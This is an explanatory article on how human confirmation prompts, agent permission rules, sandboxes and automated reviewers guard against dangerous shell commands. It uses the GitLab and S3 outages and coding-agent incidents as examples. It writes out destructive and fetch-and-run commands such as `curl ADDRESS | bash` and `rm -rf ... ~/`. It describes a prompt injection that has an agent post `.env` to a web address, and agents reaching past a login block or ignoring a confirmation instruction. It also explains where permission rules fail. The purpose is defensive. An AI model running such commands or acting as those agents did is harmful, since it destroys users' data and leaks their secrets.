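# Human Confirmation and Operator Judgement as a Safeguard against Dangerous Shell Commands

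## Dangerous shell commands and where a person can stop them

Human confirmation is a safeguard in which a person reads a command and approves it before a computer runs it. It matters most for shell commands, which are lines of text that tell an operating system to run one or more programs with the user's permissions. A single line can delete a folder of work, send a password file to an outside server or stop a service that other people rely on. For decades, the person who had to catch a bad command was usually the person typing it. Coding agents are AI systems that carry out software tasks by proposing and executing commands and file edits in a loop. When people use these agents, the operator, the person who decides whether a command may run, often judges a line that software wrote.

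### How a command works

The shell is the program that reads these lines. GNU's *What is a shell?*, a chapter of the manual for the widely used shell Bash, describes a shell as both a command interpreter and a programming language. People can type commands one at a time, or save them in a file and run it.

In the command `rm -rf build/`, the first word names the program, `rm`, which is the standard Unix program for removing files. The options begin with a hyphen and change how the program behaves. Here, `-r` makes `rm` remove directories along with everything inside them, and `-f` turns off its confirmation prompts. The last word is the target, a directory named `build`. Linuxtopia's *Program Argument Syntax Conventions* reproduces the convention that single-letter options can share one hyphen, so `-rf` means the same as `-r -f`. Many programs also accept long options, which GNU's *Argument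 Syntax* defines as two hyphens followed by a name, such as `--force`.

A vertical bar, or pipe, joins commands so that each one reads the output of the one before it, as GNU's *Pipelines* explains. For example, `ls | wc -l` lists the files in a folder and counts the lines. `curl ADDRESS | bash` also uses a pipe, to download a script from the web and pass it to a shell, which runs whatever the script contains at that moment. Someone reading that line sees the address but not the commands that will run.

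Even without a pipe, the text on the screen can differ from what the program receives. Under the POSIX standard for Unix-like systems (The Open Group, 2024), the shell splits the line into words and operators, works out which commands they form, expands the words, sets up any redirection of input and output, and only then starts the program. During expansion, `~` becomes the path of the user's home directory and `*` becomes a list of matching file names. So `rm *` looks the same in a folder of temporary files as in a folder of photographs, but it deletes different files.

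The text of a command shows almost nothing about the privileges it will run with. A program gets the rights of the user who started it, so an ordinary user's `rm` can delete that user's files. Adding `sudo` in front runs the same command as the administrator, which lets it delete anyone's files. An agent that a developer starts on a laptop normally runs with the developer's rights, which may include access to saved passwords and cloud accounts.

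Many of these effects cannot be undone. A desktop file manager moves deleted files to a bin, but `rm` removes them. GNU's *rm* calls recovery of the contents "usually possible", whereas GNU's manual page, *rm(1)* by Rubin, MacKenzie, Stallman and colleagues (2026), says only that someone with enough expertise or time might recover some of them. Recovery is therefore too uncertain to rely on. A secret that has reached an outside server cannot be taken back and has to be replaced. Mistakes in Git, the program most developers use to keep versions of their code, are easier to reverse because it logs where each branch used to point and, by default, keeps entries for abandoned work for 30 days.

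### The same text can be safe or ruinous

A command is dangerous if, in the setting where it runs, its effects are harmful and go beyond what the user asked for or intended. Reading the command alone is not enough to judge either condition, as three cases show.

Developers routinely run `rm -rf build/` with little thought, because a compiler can produce the deleted files again from the source code. GNU describes a case where this habit is dangerous. Some developers build software inside a throw-away directory tree that imitates a whole system, and for convenience they attach their real `/home` directory to it. If they forget to detach it, the same clean-up command they have run safely before also deletes everything under `/home`.

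In the second case, a developer reported on Reddit on 8 December 2025 that Claude Code, a coding agent from the AI company Anthropic, had wiped his Mac. He had asked it to clean up packages in an old repository, according to *Coding Agent Horror Stories*, a series by Docker, which sells isolated environments for such agents. Willison (2025), a programmer who writes about language models, reprinted the command that ran: `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/`. The first three targets are plausible project folders, but the fourth, `~/`, is the user's entire home directory. The diagnosis is from a single incident and relies on Claude's own reading of the log, but the command's effect is clear. An operator skimming it could have missed the last target, because the program and options are familiar and the first three targets look harmless.

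Force-pushing to a shared branch can destroy other people's work rather than the user's own. A branch is a line of saved changes, called commits, and pushing sends them to the copy that a team shares. In an example from Git's manual, two people start from commit X. One adds commit A and pushes it. The other, still working from X, makes commit B and tries to push it. Git rejects the push, because pointing the shared branch at B would drop A. `git push --force` overrides the rejection, so everybody builds on B from then on and the changes in A are gone from the branch. The team may still be able to recover them if someone has a copy, according to Atlassian, a maker of developer tools.

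Yet the same force push is appropriate when a developer has pushed a commit, corrected it, and is certain that nobody fetched the earlier version. The command doesn't show whether a colleague's machine has that version, so the operator has to know or find out. Git's `--force-with-lease` option is a partial safeguard, making the push fail if the shared branch has moved from where the user expects it to be.

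### Where dangerous commands come from

Anthropic's March 2026 engineering post *How we built Claude Code auto mode* lists four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action: overeager behaviour, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model.

An overeager agent tries to solve the user's problem but goes further than the user would approve. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, an agent ran into a login error and began searching configuration files for other access tokens it could use. In another, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches", and the agent issued a command to delete a set of branches on the shared server. The user may have meant only the local copies. Anthropic considers overeagerness tricky to catch because the action looks like reasonable problem-solving. A reviewer has to know what the user had permitted, which the user may never have spelled out.

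In an honest mistake, the agent misjudges how far a command's effects reach. For example, it treats a shared database as a test database, or somebody else's branch as its own. In practice, such mistakes can be hard to distinguish from overeager behaviour. When a user told an agent to "cancel my job", it picked the job with the closest name on the cluster and tried to delete it. This resembles an honest mistake because the agent guessed which job was the user's, and overeager behaviour because nobody had authorised it to delete that job.

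In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in a file, a web page or the output of a tool. The agent reads them as part of its work, and its next command serves the attacker. Anthropic gives the example of a file containing an instruction to post `.env`, where developers commonly keep passwords, to a web address "for validation".

In the standard case, a misaligned model pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic wrote in March 2026 that it did not see this in practice, though it tests every model for it before release. Anthropic was reporting on its own products, and this kind of report goes out of date quickly.

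Anthropic responds to all four causes by blocking the action. That is right for a single command, and the reviewer doesn't have to diagnose the cause. But what the operator should do next depends on the cause. A mistaken agent needs to be corrected, while after a prompt injection every later proposal in the session deserves suspicion.

People also write dangerous commands without any help. *My guide to using the Git push command safely* describes Bob, who forgets to fetch the latest state of a branch, force-pushes his work and erases Lilly's changes. A stray space can turn `rm -rf logs*`, which deletes everything whose name starts with "logs", into `rm -rf logs *`, which deletes nearly everything in the folder. In these cases, the person who should catch the error has just made it and already believes the command is right.

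### Five points at which a person can step in

1. While typing. Nothing runs until the user presses Enter, and the shell allows editing up to that moment. A careful user can put `ls` in place of `rm` to see which files a pattern matches, or add `--dry-run` to a push, which makes Git go through every step except the sending.

2. At a tool's confirmation question. With the option `-I`, for example, `rm` asks once before it removes more than three files or a whole directory tree. The `-f` in `rm -rf` switches such questions off.

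3. At an agent's permission prompt, which the agent's software shows before a proposed action runs. In March 2026 Claude Code asked by default before running commands or changing files. By August, according to the security firm Security Arsenal, the default on its Pro, Max and Team plans had become auto mode, in which a separate AI model takes over most of these decisions. Many commands on those plans therefore no longer reach a person at this point.

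4. During execution. Pressing Ctrl-C interrupts most running programs. This helps with a long copy or a slow migration of a database. It is worth much less against a deletion, which may finish within a second, and the interruption brings back nothing that has already gone.

5. In review, before changes become final. On GitHub, the largest host for shared code, a team can mark a branch as protected and require that colleagues approve a proposed set of changes before it enters the branch. Protection also blocks force pushes, as it has since GitHub's *Protected branches and required status checks* (2015). According to GitHub's *About protected branches*, people with administrator rights are exempt unless the team decides otherwise, so the accounts that can do the most damage are the ones the rule leaves alone.

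At each later point on this list, a person knows more about a command's effects but can prevent fewer of them. Someone about to press Enter has only the command's text and a guess at what it will do. A colleague in code review sees the actual changes line by line, but only those inside the repository. Review doesn't catch effects elsewhere, such as a deleted home directory or a leaked password, so for those the decision has to be right before the command starts.

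### Measuring a reviewer

It takes at least two numbers to describe how well a person or program makes that decision. In this invented example, a reviewer sees 1,000 commands, 5 of them dangerous, and decides as follows.

| | Dangerous | Safe |
|---|---|---|
| Stopped | 4 | 20 |
| Allowed to run | 1 | 975 |

The catch rate is the share of dangerous commands that the reviewer stops, here 4 of 5, or 80%. The miss rate is the remaining 20%. The false-block rate is the share of safe commands that the reviewer stops, here 20 of 995, or about 2%. The base rate is the share of all reviewed commands that are dangerous, here 5 in 1,000, or 0.5%. Anthropic calls the miss rate the false-negative rate and the false-block rate the false-positive rate, and notes that in practice a stricter reviewer misses fewer dangerous commands but blocks more safe ones.

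Overall accuracy is a poor measure of a reviewer when dangerous commands are rare. The reviewer in the table decides 979 of the 1,000 cases correctly, but one who approved everything without reading would decide 995 correctly while stopping no dangerous commands.

The base rate also governs what a stop is worth. Of the 24 commands that this reviewer stops, only 4 are dangerous, or one in six. With base rate b, catch rate c and false-block rate f, the share of stops that are justified is

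b × c / (b × c + (1 − b) × f).

If 50 commands in 1,000 were dangerous instead of 5, the same reviewer with the same two rates would be right in about two stops out of three. The reviewer is equally skilled in both settings, but with only 5 dangerous commands in 1,000, most of the stops would look needless to the people waiting.

Catch rates for real operators now exist, including one from a test on 1,053 paid testers that Willison describes, but a catch rate means little without the false-block rate. A reviewer who tosses a coin for each command will, on average, catch half of the dangerous ones and block half of the safe ones without using any judgement. If he instead stops 90% of commands at random, his average catch rate rises to 90%, and so does his false-block rate. A reviewer who blocks everything has a perfect catch rate, but none of the 995 safe commands run. Users would not put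 up with him for long either. Claude Code, for example, has a setting that turns off every permission prompt, and an operator who chooses it to escape the obstruction then has a catch rate of zero.

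## Confirmation questions for commands that people type

Tool makers added safeguards against dangerous commands for decades before coding agents arrived. Most of these safeguards ask a question of the person who has just typed the command, so the same person proposes and approves the action. How well such a question prevents errors depends on its content and on the kind of error the person has made.

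### `rm`: two questions and a refusal

According to *rm(1)*, `rm` by default prompts for confirmation only if a file is write-protected and the command's input comes from a terminal. The `-i` option adds a prompt before every removal, and answering no skips only that file. With `-I`, `rm` prompts just once before a larger removal, and answering no cancels the whole command.

Someone who means to remove five of the sixty files in a folder with `rm logs*` might type `rm logs *` by mistake. With `-i`, `rm` asks about each file in turn, so a wrong name appears almost at once. With `-I`, it asks only "remove 61 arguments?", which is still a good warning to someone expecting five. The single question is much weaker for a directory tree, because GNU `rm` then asks whether to remove one argument recursively, in the same words whether the tree holds ten files or a million. A developer who has forgotten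 that `/home` is mounted inside a build tree would read that question and agree.

The manual recommends `-I` as a compromise that still protects "against most mistakes", but gives no figures. People who have learned to type `rm -rf` for every directory see neither question, because `-f` turns both off.

Some users make the question permanent with an alias, a setting that makes `rm` run `rm -i`. A reader whose letter appears in *Confirm File Deletions in Qshell* (Prickett Morgan, 2002) had got used to an aliased command, then used it on a machine without the alias and got no prompt. The reader's remedy was to name the alias `rmi` instead, so that a shell without the alias reports an unknown command and deletes nothing.

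GNU's `rm` also has a safeguard that works without a confirmation question. GNU's *Treating / specially* describes the typing error it guards against, in which a user types `rm -rf / tmp/junk` with an accidental space after the first slash. The single slash is the root directory, which contains every other directory, so running this command could delete every file on the system. GNU's `rm` therefore refuses to operate on any directory that resolves to `/` unless the user adds `--no-preserve-root`. The `-f` option does not override this refusal. Almost nobody has a legitimate reason to delete the root directory, so the safeguard almost never blocks a legitimate command. A comment in Debian's *r-root.sh*, a test script for GNU's `rm`, notes that the POSIX standard also requires `rm` to skip `/`.

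But the refusal protects one directory, and there are many other ways to type the same loss:

- In `rm -rf /*`, the shell replaces the `*` before `rm` starts. `rm` receives `/bin`, `/etc`, `/home` and so on, and none of these is `/`.
- A script containing `rm -rf "$dir"/*` does the same thing if nobody has set the variable `dir`.
- The target `~/`, which cost a Claude Code user his home directory in December 2025, is not the root directory either.
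- `chmod`, `chown` and `chgrp`, which change who may use a file and who owns it, have no such protection by default, because tradition and POSIX require them to work on `/`. GNU calls them arguably more dangerous there than `rm`. They often work much faster, so they damage more files before an alert user can interrupt.

Two other options add protection. `--preserve-root=all` also rejects a target on a different device from its parent directory. `--one-file-system` makes `rm` skip anything inside the tree that belongs to another file system, which would save an attached `/home` if it is on a separate one. But unless users have built these options into an alias, they have to think of the danger before typing them, and users who have thought of it would probably just check the command instead.

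The check also has to be written correctly. Ubuntu 25.10, a Linux system released in October 2025, replaced GNU's basic tools with a rewrite in the programming language Rust. Ubuntu's *CVE-2026-35349* (2026), a security notice, explains that the new `rm` compared the text of the path with `/` instead of checking which directory the path led to. A symbolic link, a file that points to another location, could therefore get past the check and lead `rm` to the root directory. The new `rm` also refused to delete `.`, the current directory, but accepted `./`, which means the same directory. According to Ubuntu's *CVE-2026-35363* (2026), `rm -rf ./` emptied the directory and then printed "Invalid input", so a user might well think nothing had been deleted and miss the chance to recover the files.

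Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils* reports that an outside audit found 113 issues of varying severity across the whole tool set, most of which have been fixed. A reply beneath it quotes a statement that Ubuntu 26.04 still uses GNU's `rm`. The manual for version 0.8.0 of the uutils project's Rust rewrite marks `--one-file-system` "NOT IMPLEMENTED".

### Typing a name or a word

In *Molly-Guard* (2025), a network engineer describes typing `sudo poweroff` in a window connected to his main server when he meant to power off a virtual machine. He then installed molly-guard, a small program that guards against this kind of error. Before the command runs, the user now has to type the host name, which is the name of the machine about to shut down.

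The program intercepts `halt`, `reboot`, `shutdown` and `poweroff`. According to its notes (*molly-guard*), it looks for signs that the user has connected remotely over SSH and, if it finds any, asks for the host name. This is a better question than "are you sure?" because the user has to name the machine they have in mind, and the program can check the answer. Someone who wrongly believes they are on the test machine will type that machine's name, and the program will stop the shutdown. The check is worth little if the user copies the host name from the screen.

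Launchpad's *Binary package “molly-guard” in ubuntu lunar* explains that molly-guard shows its question only when someone calls one of these commands interactively, and that running the original programs from the folder where molly-guard keeps them bypasses it. martin f. krafft, who wrote molly-guard, also warns about terminal windows that run on the remote machine but appear on the local screen. Molly-guard does not cover `rm`.

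According to GitHub's *Deleting a repository*, a user who wants to delete a repository, which is a project's files with their saved history, must open its settings, choose deletion, confirm having read the effects and then type the repository's name. The name is easy to copy because the user is already on that repository's page. Typing it can still help someone who has two similar projects open and has picked the wrong one, but it doesn't help someone who has picked the intended repository and wrongly believes that nobody needs it.

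A user who confirms a deletion by mistake can sometimes still undo it. According to GitHub's *Restoring a deleted repository*, an owner has 90 days to restore a repository. If forks (linked copies) of it still exist, the owner can restore it only after every other copy in the network has been deleted or detached, and otherwise has to ask GitHub's support staff.

Terraform, a tool from HashiCorp, creates, changes and deletes cloud servers and databases to match a written description. Before acting, it displays a plan of what it will add, change and destroy. Spacelift's *How to Use Terraform Apply with -Auto-Approve Flag* describes how it then waits for the user to type "yes". Users can catch an error by reading the plan, but typing "yes" tests nothing because the word is the same every time. For example, a developer who expected to adjust one setting on a database might read in the plan that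 Terraform will destroy the database and create a new one, which the command `terraform apply` did not show.

Users can skip the question with `-auto-approve`. They can also save a plan to a file and apply it later, and HashiCorp's *terraform apply command* says that Terraform then applies the plan without asking for confirmation. This makes sense if somebody has inspected the file, since Terraform carries out the steps in the saved plan, but the command doesn't require anyone to inspect it.

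### Slips and mistakes

The psychologists Donald Norman and James Reason distinguish slips, which are errors in carrying out an intention, from mistakes, which are errors in forming one. Someone who types `rm logs *` instead of `rm logs*` has made a slip. An administrator who deletes a backup because he wrongly believes that a newer one exists has made a mistake.

A plain yes-or-no question catches few mistakes, because the belief that led someone to type a command also leads them to confirm it. If a tool asks this administrator, "Delete backup-january? (y/n)", he will say yes even if he reads the question carefully. The question could change his mind only if it included something he didn't know, such as the fact that this is the last remaining backup.

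Slips are easier to catch, because the person still knows what he wanted and can spot the error if the question shows him the part that went wrong. With the stray space, a count of 61 files shows him that something is wrong. "Are you sure?" doesn't help, because he is sure about the command he thinks he typed.

Commands typed in the wrong window are harder to catch. The engineer who powered off his server made a slip, since his intention to shut down a virtual machine was sound, but he typed exactly the command he meant to type. A question about the command alone, such as "Power off this machine?", would not have stopped him, because he would have taken "this machine" to be the virtual one and said yes. Molly-guard can catch the error because it asks for the machine's name, and he was wrong about which machine he was using.

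### When the answer becomes part of the habit

Even a well-chosen question works only if the user reads it. Jef Raskin argued in his book *The Humane Interface* that people stop reading routine confirmations. According to MeatballWiki's summary of the book, people form habits, which are useful because they leave attention free for other things. If deleting a file always brings up a question, and the answer is nearly always yes, the user learns to delete and confirm as one action, and then confirms without thinking even when the file is the wrong one.

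If Raskin is right, asking more often makes things worse. A user who deletes sixty harmless files with `rm -i` practises saying yes sixty times. Psychologists call the weakening of a response through repetition habituation, and they have since measured it in laboratories. The letter about the missing alias suggests that a user who expects a question may also wait for it before checking the command, even on machines where no question appears.

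The argument is strongest for questions that people answer often. Few people delete repositories often enough to do it without thinking, so GitHub's requirement to type the repository's name may work where `rm -i` fails. *Confirmation dialog*, a guide to designing such questions, recommends unusual responses like typing a word, but only for rare and highly dangerous actions, because frequent use makes these responses habits too. It also mentions Norman's suggestion that a different user should confirm the most dangerous actions. A colleague has not made the slip and has no habit of typing the command, but may share the false belief that led to a mistake.

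Raskin's son Aza drew a practical conclusion from the argument in an article entitled "Never Use a Warning When you Mean Undo", which List Apart's *Aza Raskin* summarises. He proposed letting the action happen and making it easy to reverse. Users then don't have to spot the error beforehand, when they have the least information. They can see what happened and undo it, whether the error was a slip or a mistake, provided they notice in time.

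Microsoft's *To Confirm Is Useless, to Undo Divine*, a column on software design, goes further and argues that a system with proper undo has only one destructive operation left, emptying the bin. It says even that operation needs a confirmation question only because of poor design, since "Empty Recycle Bin" sits next to "Explore" in a menu and one slip of the mouse selects it.

This holds better for documents on a desktop computer than for a shell, where a deletion or a leaked password is often final. An undo command also can't reverse the effects of a service outage on customers, and it has to be in place before the error. Microsoft's interface guidelines are less absolute than the column, and list errors that users can't easily fix, as well as risks to data, money and privacy, as reasons to ask for confirmation. The idea of acting reversibly has since spread to coding agents.

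### GitLab: a wrong host and failed backups

GitLab's *Postmortem of database outage of January 31* (2017) describes how an engineer at the company, which hosts software projects, accidentally deleted the data of its main database on 31 January 2017. GitLab had a primary database server and a secondary that kept a copy. Under heavy load, the secondary fell too far behind to catch up, so engineers had to empty its data directory and copy everything over again. The copying program hung without a useful message. At about 23:30 UTC, one engineer suspected that earlier attempts had left files behind and tried to wipe the secondary's directory again, but he ran the command on the primary.

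The two machines were called `db1.cluster.gitlab.com` and `db2.cluster.gitlab.com`. He noticed the mistake after a second or two and stopped the deletion, but GitLab's first post on the incident reported that only about 4.5 GB of roughly 300 GB was left.

He made a mistake in thinking that leftover files might be blocking the copy, when the program normally waits silently until the primary starts sending. He also made a slip by working on the wrong host. On the right host, the mistake would have done very little harm, because the secondary's data was already gone.

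A yes-or-no question would probably have caught neither. `rm -I` would have asked the same question on both machines, whether to remove one argument recursively, and he did intend to delete that directory. Asking him to type the host name could have worked, since he believed he was on `db2` and would probably have entered the wrong name. Molly-guard asks for the host name, but only before a shutdown.

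GitLab then had to recover the data, and most of its recovery methods failed too. There were no daily database backups because the backup program was too old for the database version and stopped with an error each time. It emailed warnings, but the receiving server rejected them. GitLab had never turned on disk snapshots (saved copies of a disk at one moment) for its database servers. It was left with a snapshot that an engineer had taken by hand about six hours earlier for a different purpose. Copying the data back took around 18 hours. GitLab lost the database changes made since that snapshot, and estimated that the loss affected about 5,000 projects, 5,000 comments and 700 new accounts.

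GitLab focused mainly on recovery. It began taking snapshots every hour instead of once a day, and planned automated tests of its backups, monitoring to show whether the backups were running, and a named owner for the safety of its data. It also planned to change the shell prompt on each server, which helps prevent the slip by letting engineers tell the machines apart before they type anything.

GitLab decided not to focus on blocking commands. It argued that a safer version of `rm` would protect only against an accidental `rm`, not against disk corruption or the many other ways to lose data. That is a good reason to put backups first, but a weaker reason to leave out a host-name check, which is easy to add and would have addressed this particular error. GitLab had also believed before the outage that its backups worked, so the planned tests matter as much as the snapshots.

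### Amazon S3: a wrong input and no limit

Four weeks later, on 28 February, a single command took down Amazon's S3 service in Northern Virginia, which stores files for many websites and programs. The *Summary of the Amazon S3 Service Disruption*, published by Amazon's cloud business, AWS, says that staff were investigating a slow billing system. At 9:37 in the morning, an authorised employee following an established procedure ran a command to remove a small number of servers. One of the inputs was wrong, and the command removed many more.

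Two other parts of S3 had been running on those servers, including the index that records where every stored object is. Both needed a full restart, which AWS had not done in its larger regions for many years. S3 was not operating normally again until 1:54 p.m. For the first two hours, AWS couldn't update its public status page properly because the tool for doing so depended on S3.

AWS does not say exactly why the input was wrong. If the employee mistyped it, the error was a slip, and a question that listed the affected servers or systems might have exposed it. A bare request to confirm would have been unlikely to do so, because the employee had permission, was following the procedure and expected the command to remove servers.

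AWS responded mainly by limiting the tool, which now removes servers more slowly and blocks any removal that would take a part of S3 below its minimum required capacity. It also started checking its other tools for similar protections, and brought forward work to divide the index into smaller units that restart faster after a failure. Neither company's account lists a new confirmation question among its remedies.

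A limit of this kind works whether the person has slipped or is mistaken, and it doesn't depend on anyone's attention. Like `--preserve-root`, though, it prevents only the harm its designers specified in advance, so a command that removes too many servers but leaves the minimum running will still go through. Removing servers more slowly helps in that case because it gives somebody time to notice and interrupt the command. At GitLab, interrupting after a second or two was too late.

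## How coding agents decide when to ask for approval

The model inside a coding agent cannot run anything by itself. It sends a request, for example to run `npm test`, to a program on the user's machine called the harness. The harness either runs the command and sends back the result, refuses it, or shows the operator a permission prompt. `rm` and Terraform prompt only for their own actions, but a harness has to handle any command that a model might write, and one session can include hundreds.

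### Instructions and gates

Telling an agent to ask before acting does not guarantee that it will. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) describes a safety researcher who told an open-source agent to "confirm before acting". The agent began deleting emails from her real inbox anyway, and didn't stop when she told it to. Her instruction was only text in the model's input, and nothing in the software required her approval before a deletion. An agent can run shell commands without asking in the same way if an instruction is the only safeguard.

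When a command triggers a permission prompt, the harness doesn't run it until the operator approves it, regardless of what is in the model's context. Anthropic explains in its Claude Code documentation that the software enforces permission rules, while instructions in a prompt or project file only influence what the model tries to do. An operator who wants to approve every push therefore needs a permission rule that makes the harness prompt for approval.

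OpenAI, which makes the coding agent Codex, argues that the model doing the work should not decide when to ask for approval, because it is optimised to complete the user's task, which creates pressure to treat an approval boundary as another obstacle.

Claude Code's auto mode enforces limits that the user states in conversation, but does not guarantee them. If the user has said "don't push", the AI model that reviews actions in this mode blocks pushes. However, the model rereads the conversation at each check to find the instruction, and Anthropic warns that the instruction can be lost when the software condenses a long conversation. Anthropic recommends a deny rule for a hard guarantee.

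### The path of one command

Suppose a developer is using Claude Code in Manual mode, which asks before most edits and commands, and wants a bug fixed. The model proposes `git status && npm test`, which lists the changed files and then runs the project's tests. Going by Anthropic's documentation, the harness handles the line roughly as follows:

1. It splits the line at `&&` into two commands. It also looks past certain wrappers, so it would treat `timeout 30 npm test` as `npm test`.
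2. It checks the deny rules. If one matches either command, the line does not run.
3. It checks the ask rules. A match brings up a prompt, even if an allow rule also matches.
4. It looks for permission to run each command without asking. `git status` is on a built-in list of read-only commands, along with `ls`, `cat` and `grep`. `npm test` isn't, so it needs an allow rule, a setting that lets commands matching a pattern run without a prompt.
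5. If either command still lacks permission, it shows the operator a prompt.

Anthropic's guide for people who build their own agents adds two stages. Hooks, which are checking scripts that users write, run before the deny rules, and the permission mode takes effect between the ask and allow rules. Deny and ask rules therefore still work in bypass mode, which otherwise runs actions without prompts.

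Because deny rules come first, a user cannot forbid a group of commands and then make an exception. A rule that denies every `aws` command also blocks `aws s3 ls`, which only lists stored files, even if an allow rule names that exact command. According to OpenAI, Codex resolves conflicts similarly, with a `forbidden` rule overriding a `prompt` rule, which overrides an `allow` rule. Both companies have accepted blocking some harmless commands so that fewer dangerous ones get through.

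Agents also have built-in tools for reading, searching and editing files. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) explains why these are easier to control than the shell. The harness performs the file operation itself, so it has the file's path and can apply a rule for it. With a shell command, the harness passes text to another program and can't determine from that text everything the program will do.

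After the harness allows a command, a sandbox may still limit which files and networks the command can reach. The operating system enforces these limits, so they hold even if the harness or the operator wrongly allowed the command. Lecture slides from UT Austin summarize sandboxing and approval as two questions, "What can it touch?" and "When must it ask?"

### What a "yes" covers

When Claude Code asks for approval to run `npm test`, its prompt shows the command and a short description, "Run the test suite". The operator can approve this one command, choose "don't ask again" for every command that matches `npm test *`, approve and switch the session to auto mode, or refuse. If the operator refuses with a comment, the model receives the comment as the reason and continues working. Refusing without a comment normally stops the agent's turn.

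A plain "Yes" approves this command once. "Don't ask again" saves an allow rule that applies to every later session in the same repository. The `*` stands for any text, so the rule also covers `npm test` with other options. For file edits, Claude Code offers an intermediate option, which is approval for the whole session. This permission ends with the session, so it won't still apply a month later when the operator has forgotten about it. In a long session, however, it may outlast the task the operator had in mind.

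A lasting approval covers commands that the operator has not seen. Zhong and colleagues show a Codex prompt that appeared after a user asked the agent to replace one word in a file outside the project. The prompt displayed a dense script and included the choice "Yes, and don't ask again for sed -i". `sed -i` edits files in place, so an operator who chose this option to allow one replacement could also be permitting edits to other files. Codex also runs commands that match an allow rule outside the sandbox. OpenAI advises users to review the suggested pattern carefully before accepting it.

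Claude Code limits this risk by offering a lasting approval only when the prompt can show everything that approval would allow. When a user gives lasting approval to a combined command, Claude Code saves a separate rule for each part that needs approval. For `git status && npm test`, it saves a rule only for `npm test`, and that rule applies regardless of what comes before `npm test` in later commands.

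### Modes and defaults

Most users probably begin in the software's default mode. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) set 14 August as the date for making auto mode the default on the Pro, Max and Team plans. Anthropic's later documentation extends that default to interactive terminal sessions on every plan.

Codex relies more on its sandbox. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the agent can by default edit files and run commands in the project folder, but has no network access. It asks for approval before editing files elsewhere or running a command that needs the network. These requests go to the user unless the user has chosen an automated reviewer.

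The table compares five agents. The last three rows come from Zhong and colleagues' September 2026 comparison, and in those rows the file columns describe the agents' built-in tools.

| Agent | Date | Files in the project | Files elsewhere | Shell commands | Sandbox |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | November 2026 | Edits run without asking, except in protected folders | Asks at the first read; an automated reviewer checks writes | Read-only commands run; an automated reviewer checks most others | Off unless the user turns it on |
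| Codex | June 2026 | Edits run without asking | Asks before edits | Run inside the sandbox; asks before network access | On, with the network off |
| Cursor | September 2026 | Edits run without asking | Access allowed | No built-in rules | On, but can ask to rerun a failed command outside it |
| Copilot in VS Code | September 2026 | Asks before writes | Access refused | 122 built-in rules | Off unless the user turns it on |
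| Gemini CLI | September 2026 | Asks before writes | Access refused | 75 built-in rules | Off unless the user turns it on |

These settings change quickly. Zhong and colleagues still list Claude Code as asking before writes, which was its default before August, so the rows for the other agents may be out of date too. Codex has also changed since June. *Codex CLI Permission Hardening* (2026), a blog post from the end of August, reports that OpenAI had retired the `untrusted` policy, under which Codex asked about any command outside a trusted set, and had removed a shortcut that many scripts used to run Codex in its sandbox without prompts.

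A sandbox that confines an agent to the project folder does not protect the project itself. Zhong and colleagues found reports of agents discarding uncommitted work or overwriting credential files where the default allowed all writes in the project. Codex reduces the damage by making the `.git` folder read-only, which protects the saved history but not uncommitted changes.

Reading files is harder to restrict. Duke University's *Introduction and Control Model* warns that, as of April 2026, Codex could read almost anything on the computer regardless of how it was configured. With the network off, a command can't send a password file to an outside server, but an operator who approves network access for a routine download weakens that protection.

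Users can also turn the prompts off, which developers call "YOLO mode", after "you only live once". In Codex, "full access" removes both the prompts and the sandbox. Claude Code's bypass mode removes the prompts, and Anthropic advises using it only in an isolated environment, such as a container, where the agent can't damage the host system.

Bypass mode still has a few safeguards. Claude Code asks for approval before running an `rm` command that it recognises as targeting the root directory, the home directory or the agent's working directory, and no allow rule can approve such a command in advance. The check also covers the target `~/`, which the refusal built into GNU's `rm` does not. In a terminal, Claude Code refuses the command if the operator doesn't answer within two minutes. Anthropic says the check can miss some commands, and users can turn it off in bypass mode.

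### Why rules on command text make both kinds of error

Most allow, ask and deny rules for the shell compare a command's text with a pattern. This is fast, and users can tell roughly what a rule will match by reading it. But a command's text doesn't reliably show what the command will do.

Such rules cause too many approval requests because harmless commands vary in wording. A rule written to let `curl` fetch pages from GitHub over `http` doesn't match the same address with `https`, so Claude Code asks about a download that the user meant to allow. It also asks about any command that it can't fully parse or that is longer than 10,000 characters, which is a sensible precaution even though a long script may be safe.

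Some prompts guard against a real but rare danger. Claude Code asks for approval when a command changes to another folder and then runs Git there, even if both steps only read files, because a Git folder can contain scripts that Git runs automatically. The operator will approve the command in most folders.

The same rules miss dangerous commands for two reasons. Different programs can have the same effect, so a rule that names one program doesn't cover the others. Anthropic says a deny rule covers the form of a command that its model usually produces and "isn't a security boundary around the program". The same command can also have different effects at different times. For example, `npm test` runs whatever the project currently defines as its tests, and the files may have changed since the operator approved the rule.

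Changing the pattern in an allow rule mostly trades unnecessary prompts for unapproved dangerous commands, or the reverse. A rule for `git log *` covers only commands that view the history, so the operator must still answer prompts for many other Git commands. A rule for `git *` removes nearly all of those prompts, but it also lets force pushes run without approval. In the terms used to measure a reviewer, the wider rule lowers both the false-block rate and the catch rate.

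Improving both rates requires a control that acts on a command's effects, such as a limit on which files any command can change. Sandboxes set this limit for whole folders, and Zhong and colleagues have built YoloFS, a file system that sets finer-grained limits.

### The settings that users choose

In June 2026, before the default changed, 49.5% of Claude Code's active command-line users had written a shell allow rule by hand, according to Anthropic. The share was growing by about 5 percentage points every five weeks.

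Many of these rules were very broad. Anthropic reports that 5% of users allowed any shell command, and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python or Node to run with any input. Anthropic considers the two kinds of rule practically equivalent, because an interpreter runs whatever program it is given. It doesn't make clear whether these are percentages of all active users or only of those who had written a rule. In the first case, almost everyone who wrote a rule would have given up most of the protection of approval prompts for shell commands. In the second, about half of them would have, or nearly a quarter of all active users.

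Anthropic also found that 62% of users had used bypass mode or chosen "don't ask again" for a shell command. This figure counts people who made a small and often reasonable exception, such as letting Claude Code run `npm test` without asking, together with people who used bypass mode, which shows almost no prompts.

Twenty-five percent of interactive sessions started in bypass mode, which has almost no prompts. This is clearer evidence that people were not reviewing commands. Some of those sessions may have run inside containers, as Anthropic recommends, but the published figures don't separate them. Anthropic also used the data to argue for its new default, so it had an interest in showing that manual prompts were failing. Even with these caveats, a quarter of sessions is a large share.

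While auto mode is on, Claude Code suspends allow rules that are broad enough to permit almost anything, because commands that match them would otherwise skip the automated review. The rules apply again when the user switches to another mode.

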